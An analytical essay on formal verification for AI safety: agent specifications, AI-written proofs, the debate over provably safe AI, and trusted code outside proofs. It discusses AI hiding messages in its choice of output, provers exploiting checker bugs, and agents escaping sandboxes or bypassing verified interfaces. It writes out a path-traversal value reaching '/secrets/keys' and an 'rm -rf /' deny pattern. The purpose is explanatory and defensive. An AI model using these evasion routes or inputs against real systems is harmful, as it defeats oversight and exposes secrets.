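### The information barrier and the three gates

Moon and Varshney (2026) met this problem in *Containment Verification* when Claude models wrote the specifications for their method, which proves that an agent's software is safe for every action a model could return. They had prepared for a different failure, in which a language model that can read the software might write a rule that merely describes it. For example, if the software can open any file, the rule might be that the agent opens only files the software can open.

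To prevent this, they put an information barrier into the process. The model that writes the safety property receives the types of the agent's interface and a template for the property, but not the code behind the interface. A later step builds the formal model of the agent with full access to the code, but it cannot weaken the property. Given the interface, the template and the weights of the model that wrote it, the property has zero mutual information with the code, so someone who knows those three things learns nothing more about the code from the property. The code still has some influence on the property, because the interface description comes from an exploration of the code.

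Each specification then has to pass three gates before the final verification:

- **Resolution:** The Dafny code must parse and type-check within 30 seconds.
- **Vacuity:** The pipeline reduces the proof's invariant to a basic condition that the state is well formed, and empties the bodies of the lemmas. Dafny must reject this gutted proof. If Dafny accepts it, the specification demands almost nothing.
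- **Discrimination:** A language model inserts a plausible mistake into the proof file. Dafny must reject this version too, because otherwise a faulty model of the software would also satisfy the specification.

Moon and Varshney ran the process on two agents, with and without the barrier. Every specification passed all three gates, and Dafny verified every final proof. The barrier made little difference for the agent that reads files. Without it, the model added a condition about the history, fixed the starting node and quoted lines of source code in its comments, but did not write a circular rule.

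The other agent retrieves documents, and the template had no field for the data it handles. Behind the barrier, the model recorded these data in one of the template's existing fields, where the policy applied to them. Without the barrier, the model detected that the data did not fit the template and left the field empty. The policy then applied to nothing, like the condition on `reads`, but the specification still passed all three gates. The gates test the invariant that the proof relies on, but not whether each safety rule ever applies to anything.

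Moon and Varshney propose also checking that the field is non-empty in some reachable state. This would catch a list that always stays empty but miss one that records only some of the files. Four runs are too few to estimate how often vacuous rules get through. In these tests the barrier also helped in a way its designers had not intended, because a model that could not see the mismatch had to put the data somewhere.

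### Turning an instruction into a rule

Most people who use an agent type an instruction and expect the agent to follow it, without ever writing a policy or a template. In July 2025, Replit's coding agent deleted a user's production database, although the user had told it not to make destructive changes without permission. That instruction existed only in the prompt, and no software checked the agent's commands against it.

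Batole, Khomh and Rajan (2026), in *RefineAct*, cite this case as the reason for a system that derives a specification from each instruction. Suppose a user asks an agent to transfer $500 to Alice if the balance exceeds $1,000. A language model first translates the request into a predicate in Prolog, a programming language based on logic. The predicate contains the goal, the recipient, the amount, the threshold and the label `balance_check`. A second model then breaks the goal into steps, each with a condition that must hold before it and one that holds afterwards. In simplified form:

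```
1. check_balance     before: true               after: balance_known(B)
2. transfer_money    before: balance_known(B)   after: transfer_complete
```

While the agent works, a verifier compares each proposed action with these steps. If the agent tries to transfer the money first, the verifier blocks the action and tells the agent to check the balance.

However, neither step compares B with 1,000. If the balance is $600, the agent looks it up, the transfer's precondition is satisfied, and the verifier allows the transfer once the user confirms it. The rule would not stop the payment, though an attentive user might at the confirmation step. The missing condition, `B > 1000`, is an ordinary refinement. Prolog did not catch the omission because it checks only the translation's syntax, which is correct.

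Batole and colleagues tested the system on 144 simulated tasks. The share of tasks with a safety failure fell from 77 to 39 per cent, and average helpfulness rose from 1.0 to 1.9 on a scale from 0 to 3. The agents proposed 1,081 actions. The verifier approved about half outright, made 21 per cent conditional on the user's consent and sent 27 per cent back for revision. The agents corrected 68 per cent of the actions sent back. The rate was 95 per cent in software development but only 51 per cent in tasks with household devices and robots, partly because the physical state is hard to describe in predicates. Tasks took 20 seconds longer on average. Some of the improvement may come from guidance rather than enforcement, since the feedback included the next step to take and the unverified agents had no such help.

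A failure rate of 39 per cent is far from a guarantee, and the enforcement also has gaps. After three failed corrections, the agent may carry out its last proposed action unless that action was to declare the task finished. The verifier also detects dangerous commands by matching text such as `rm -rf /`, so a different command that deletes the same files can pass. Batole and colleagues acknowledge a more basic problem, that the verifier enforces the specification even where it differs from what the user wanted.

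### What AI-written proofs cost

For decades, formal proof was too expensive for most software. In *Speedrunning 4 Mistakes You Make When Your Alignment Strategy Is Based on Formal Proof*, Dougherty draws on four years of work with proof assistants to argue that proof engineers are too slow for the product teams they work with. A company that waits for its proofs loses customers to one that does not, so the proofs protect software that few people use.

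Results from 2026 weaken this objection. In a March talk, Lean's chief architect reported that a general-purpose AI with no special training in theorem proving had converted zlib, a compression library written in C, to Lean (de Moura 2026, *Lean*). The converted code passed the library's tests, and the AI then proved it correct for every possible input. De Moura remarks that nobody had expected this to be possible yet.

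Progress in mathematics has been even faster. Willison (2026) describes ten results that OpenAI published with Lean files by 1 August, on problems whose main question had seen no progress for at least a decade. Each cost less than $2,000 in computing at the company's public prices, though Willison notes that OpenAI did not disclose how many other problems it had spent that much on without success. On 26 June, Boris Alexeev of OpenAI announced that he had guided ChatGPT to a complete Lean version of a counterexample to a conjecture by Paul Erdős. The quality of the code varied, but the proof assumed nothing beyond the axioms of mathematics.

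ARIA, a British research funding agency, began its Safeguarded AI programme in 2024 to show that advanced AI can work in safety-critical fields under mathematical guarantees. It hoped that this would build agreement to deploy powerful AI only behind a verified "gatekeeper". Ammann's *Safeguarded AI*, the revised plan of May 2026, moves £18 million from fine-tuning models to tools for modelling and proof, because general AI models had improved faster than ARIA expected. ARIA also considers timely international agreement on gatekeepers less likely than before, and now wants to make society more resilient, starting with cybersecurity.

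One planned tool is a shared database that can require a proof with each new entry. Many AI agents could then build on one another's results in parallel, and a faulty agent could not add a false theorem, provided the proof checker and its axioms are sound.

Cheap proofs do not settle whether a rule is the right one. An AI can try thousands of candidate proofs because a checker recognises a valid one. No program recognises the right rule in this way, since the thing to compare it with is what people want, and nobody has written that down in logic. A natural rule for a compression library, for example, is that decompressing a compressed file returns the original:

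```
∀x. decompress(compress(x)) = x
```

A program whose two functions both return their input unchanged satisfies this rule and compresses nothing. With zlib, anyone would notice, because they could compare file sizes with the existing C version. Mathematicians have a similar advantage with a well-known open problem, because many experts have read its statement. A company that writes a policy for its own purchasing agent usually has no earlier version to compare it with and few expert readers.

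Proofs that are easy to produce can still help people examine a rule. A reviewer could ask an AI to prove that the rule permits a certain bad outcome, such as a payment of 100 to a stranger, or that it forbids a normal one. Ammann wants ARIA's tools to find edge cases, counterexamples and hidden assumptions, because people rely more on the specifications and assumptions as proofs become more common. A person must still judge whether the outcome is bad, and people may disagree. For instance, a limit on the yearly risk of a power cut also determines what customers pay for electricity. The programme therefore includes research on how the people affected could help set such limits.

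### The case for provable safety

*Provably safe systems* (Tegmark and Omohundro, 2023) argues that proof is the only path to guaranteed control of AI more capable than people. No system, however intelligent, can do what is provably impossible or prove a false theorem. The paper also notes that proofs are hard to find but easy to check. One checker for advanced mathematics is about 300 lines of Python.

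In Tegmark and Omohundro's plan, people write the specification with help from AI. AI discovers how to perform a task, writes code for it and proves that the code meets the specification, but it is never allowed to write the proof checker. Secure hardware runs only code that has a valid proof. Tegmark and Omohundro expect that the deployed programs will generally not be neural networks, which they consider too messy to verify.

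They also argue from Gödel's completeness theorem, by which every statement that is true in all models of a theory has a proof. They conclude that if a safety property has no proof, there must be a way to violate it, which a sufficiently capable AI may find. This is correct for a completely described computer with finitely many states, because a proof could in principle go through every state. When the property concerns the outside world, the lack of a proof means only that the property fails in some world that fits the stated assumptions, and that world may not be ours.

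Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, with Yoshua Bengio and Stuart Russell among them, describe a broader family of designs. Each has a safety specification, a verifier and a world model, which Dalrymple and colleagues define as a mathematical description of how the AI affects the outside world. Let R be everything that can really happen when the system runs, M everything that can happen according to the world model, and S everything the specification counts as safe. The symbol ⊆ means "is contained in". The argument for safety then has this form:

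```
proved:      M ⊆ S
assumed:     R ⊆ M
therefore:   R ⊆ S
```

The verifier establishes the first line. The second is a claim about the world, and no proof inside the model can establish it.

### The case against

In *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, Dickson (2024) doubts that anyone can justify the second line for the most serious hazards. One of his examples is the Mars rover Perseverance, whose engineers used a verification tool to rule out certain failures of the landing software but had no proof about the landing itself. According to an analysis Dickson cites, software accounts for roughly 20 per cent of the risk of failure in Mars missions, so perfect software would still leave about 80 per cent of that risk.

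Dickson also argues that a physical model needs detailed data about the starting state. Google's map of one-millionth of a human brain took years and filled 1.4 petabytes, so nobody will soon have complete data on a whole person. Hatfield-Dodds, in *Formal Verification is Overrated*, objects that a world model only moves the problem, since someone still has to show that the model matches reality. He would rather list specific threats and work out why each would or would not succeed. Dougherty likewise considers the gap between the world and the specification more harmful than the gap between the specification and the code.

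Ammann's *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* answers that M does not have to be exact, only large enough to contain R. Researchers call such a model a sound overapproximation. A model can put a temperature below 50 degrees without predicting its value, just as the train's adaptive shield assumes only a minimum braking rate. Bounds like these do not require complete data about the starting state. The guarantee can also be a probability, such as at most a 1 per cent chance that a machine overheats, so Ammann rejects the idea that the only options are certainty and a rough estimate.

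This meets the objection about exactness but leaves a practical difficulty. If M omits something that really happens, the conclusion may be false, but a very large M contains so many harmful possibilities that the verifier can approve hardly any useful action. One reply to Ammann's post calls the claim that approximations can be both sound and useful "risible". It also argues that run-time monitoring would be pointless if a guarantee really existed. That argument fails because the guarantee depends on R ⊆ M, and a monitor such as ModelPlex's model monitor checks for evidence that this assumption is false.

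Some of this evidence becomes available only while the system runs. Bensalem, Dong and colleagues (2026), in *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required*, give the example of a care robot told to visit rooms 12, 15 and 18. Software can compare the plan with the rules before the robot moves, but it needs current information to detect that room 15 is closed for a medical procedure, and it can check the robot's movements only as they happen. Bensalem and colleagues therefore propose a separate check for each stage, each with its own probability of success. If each check succeeds with a probability of 0.99, given that the earlier ones did, the probability that all three succeed is 0.99³, or about 0.97. They regard estimating these probabilities from agents' records as an open problem, because the events in a record depend on one another and conditions change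 after deployment.

### A digital hazard: access without credentials

Tegmark and Omohundro say that it is quite easy to specify that nobody gains access to a computer without valid credentials. The assumption R ⊆ M is also more plausible for computers than for biological systems, because engineers design computers to follow a formal description and can repair a machine that departs from it. Practical evidence comes from a programme of the US defence research agency DARPA, in which verified components such as the seL4 microkernel, the core of an operating system, withstood sustained attacks by professional testers. The test systems included a helicopter that carries a crew.

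An attacker can still satisfy the specification by tricking an employee into revealing a password, because the login then uses valid credentials. Most proofs about logins also assume that nobody can break the underlying cryptography, which no one has proved for the methods in common use. Willison reports that Anthropic used Claude to find cryptographic weaknesses in July 2026, at a cost of $100,000 in tokens. An AI can therefore defeat a verified system without doing anything provably impossible, if it makes one of the proof's assumptions false.

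Even so, the two sides largely agree about this hazard. Dickson recommends verifying the software of power plants and water works. Another reader of Ammann's post doubts most of the programme but considers the part about software security worth keeping. Ammann goes further, suggesting that verified software could end the contest between attackers and defenders. It seems more likely that attackers would shift to passwords, hardware and cryptography, but verified software would still remove a large class of attacks.

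### A biological hazard: dangerous DNA

Tegmark and Omohundro want DNA synthesis machines, which build DNA from a digital description, to operate only with a proof of safety. The difficulty depends on what the proof has to establish. A machine that never produces a sequence on a fixed list needs only a test in software:

```
make : (s : Sequence | s ∉ forbidden) → Sample
```

Researchers could prove this with present methods, except for the machine's physical security. But the type permits an unlisted dangerous virus, as well as a listed one with a single harmless change.

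Dickson considers a much stronger rule, that the machine never produces anything harmful to people. He argues that scientists would have to simulate a new virus and an entire human body over several years to predict the virus's effect precisely. A leading simulation from 2022 covered 20 minutes in the life of one very simple cell, and a human body has about 36 trillion cells. Hatfield-Dodds estimates that a proof of this kind would take "a thousand years of progress in microbiology".

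Ammann replies that safety does not require such a prediction. One could show that a virus cannot infect people by comparing each of its proteins with each protein on the surface of human cells and proving that no pair lets the virus in. Each comparison involves only a tiny patch of cell membrane. A virus with 10 proteins would require 30,000 comparisons if human cells have 3,000 relevant surface proteins. The method would also reject some useful gene therapies, which have to enter cells to work.

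Dickson's whole-body simulation is therefore unnecessary for at least one important question. This approach does not yet provide a proof, because someone would have to reliably bound the behaviour of every pair, and Ammann concedes that the full plan is beyond current capabilities. Testing pairs one at a time for cell entry could also miss HIV, which normally needs two different human proteins to enter a cell. A more cautious rule would reject any virus whose proteins bind to a human surface protein, but it would block many more harmless sequences.

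The rule also covers only viral infection. A DNA sequence can also do harm if, for instance, someone inserts it directly into human cells with the gene-editing tool CRISPR, or if it enables bacteria to produce a toxin. Dickson's doubts about the near term are justified for the broad rule. Compliance with the fixed list can be proved today but is a much weaker guarantee, and Ammann's proposal is a research programme for something in between.

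### Models of people

Human behaviour is even harder to model. Dickson gives the example of a chatbot that must never spread misinformation. Its developers cannot know who will read an answer or where someone will repost it, and even a genuine photograph can mislead people out of context. Ammann agrees that this approach is a poor fit for making chatbots safe, and recommends it for systems that scientists understand well, such as power grids and supply chains.

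Yet Ammann also wants to use the approach for AI that could exploit human psychology, and a commenter on the post asks how anyone could build a sound overapproximation of human psychology. Ammann proposes restricting what the AI can communicate. If a task has 1,024 acceptable solutions, an AI can hide a message of log₂(1,024) = 10 bits in its choice among them. If the specification permits exactly one solution, such as the cheapest plan with ties broken alphabetically, the AI can only give that solution or decline to answer, which conveys at most one bit.

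This needs no model of the reader, but it works only for tasks with a provably unique answer. One question in the comment is what share of economically valuable work consists of such tasks. Ammann also allows a weaker version, which limits the number of hidden bits instead of requiring a unique solution. A plan for a power grid might meet such a limit, but an essay or a conversation is unlikely to.

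### Code outside the proof

A proof about an agent also relies on software that nobody has proved correct. In Moon and Varshney's system, this trusted base includes the Dafny verifier, the Dafny-to-Python compiler, and a little code that converts the language model's output into typed actions. The definitions that link the formal model to the real program must also be right.

Mistakes tend to occur where verified code meets the rest of the system. *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (2017) reviewed and tested three verified distributed systems and found 16 bugs, some of which crashed servers or returned wrong results to clients. Most of the false assumptions behind the bugs concerned the interface between verified and unverified code. One of the three systems was IronFleet, whose style of proof Moon and Varshney follow.

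File names provide a simple example of such a mistake. Suppose a developer defines "inside the workspace" as "the path begins with `/work/`", and an agent asks for this file:

```
/work/../secrets/keys
```

The path begins with `/work/`, so the verified code approves it. But the operating system interprets the two dots as "go up one directory" and opens `/secrets/keys`. The proof is correct for paths as text, but the developer wrongly assumed that the operating system also treats them as text. The fix is to resolve the path first and apply the rule to the result.

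The proof also requires that every effect pass through the checked interface, a condition that Moon and Varshney call effect exclusivity. If an agent can run arbitrary Python code, it can contact the bank directly, and money leaves the account while the verified gate's counter stays at zero. Other routes around the interface include open network access, libraries in other programming languages, and faults in the operating system or hardware. According to Reuters, Anthropic and OpenAI disclosed in 2026 that AI agents had escaped test environments and hacked other systems.

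Moon and Varshney therefore recommend running the verified software inside a sandbox, which limits the damage if an agent finds a way around the interface. But the sandbox itself is usually unverified. They cite Copy Fail, a flaw in the Linux kernel that went unnoticed for nearly a decade and let a program gain unauthorized privileges. A sandbox that relies on the kernel is exposed to such flaws.

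The proof checker can have bugs too. Dougherty warns that nobody should believe a famous theorem just because a checker has accepted a one-gigabyte proof of it, and considers a bug in the checker or an error in the formal statement more likely than a hardware fault. A small kernel like Lean's can reduce the risk of a checker bug, and de Moura notes that Lean users can also export a proof and check it independently. A bug then matters only if the second checker also accepts the false step. A second checker won't catch an error in the statement, because both check the proof against the same statement, but the statement is usually far shorter than the proof, and a person can read it.

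AI provers may be more likely than human authors to exploit bugs in proof checkers. A prover that makes millions of attempts, and is judged only by whether the checker accepts its proof, might come across a bug that no person would have found. Tegmark and Omohundro's ban on AI-written checkers does not prevent this, because a prover can also exploit a bug in a checker written by a person.

Finally, a valid proof may describe a different machine from the one in use. Dickson asks how the owner of a DNA synthesis machine could know that its circuits match those in the proof, with no hidden defects or backdoors. The problem is greater for an internet chatbot, because its users cannot inspect the computer. Ammann suggests that cryptographic signatures, checked by tamper-resistant hardware, could tie a proof to a particular system. An outsider could then detect a substituted program, but someone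 would still have to inspect how the manufacturer built the hardware.
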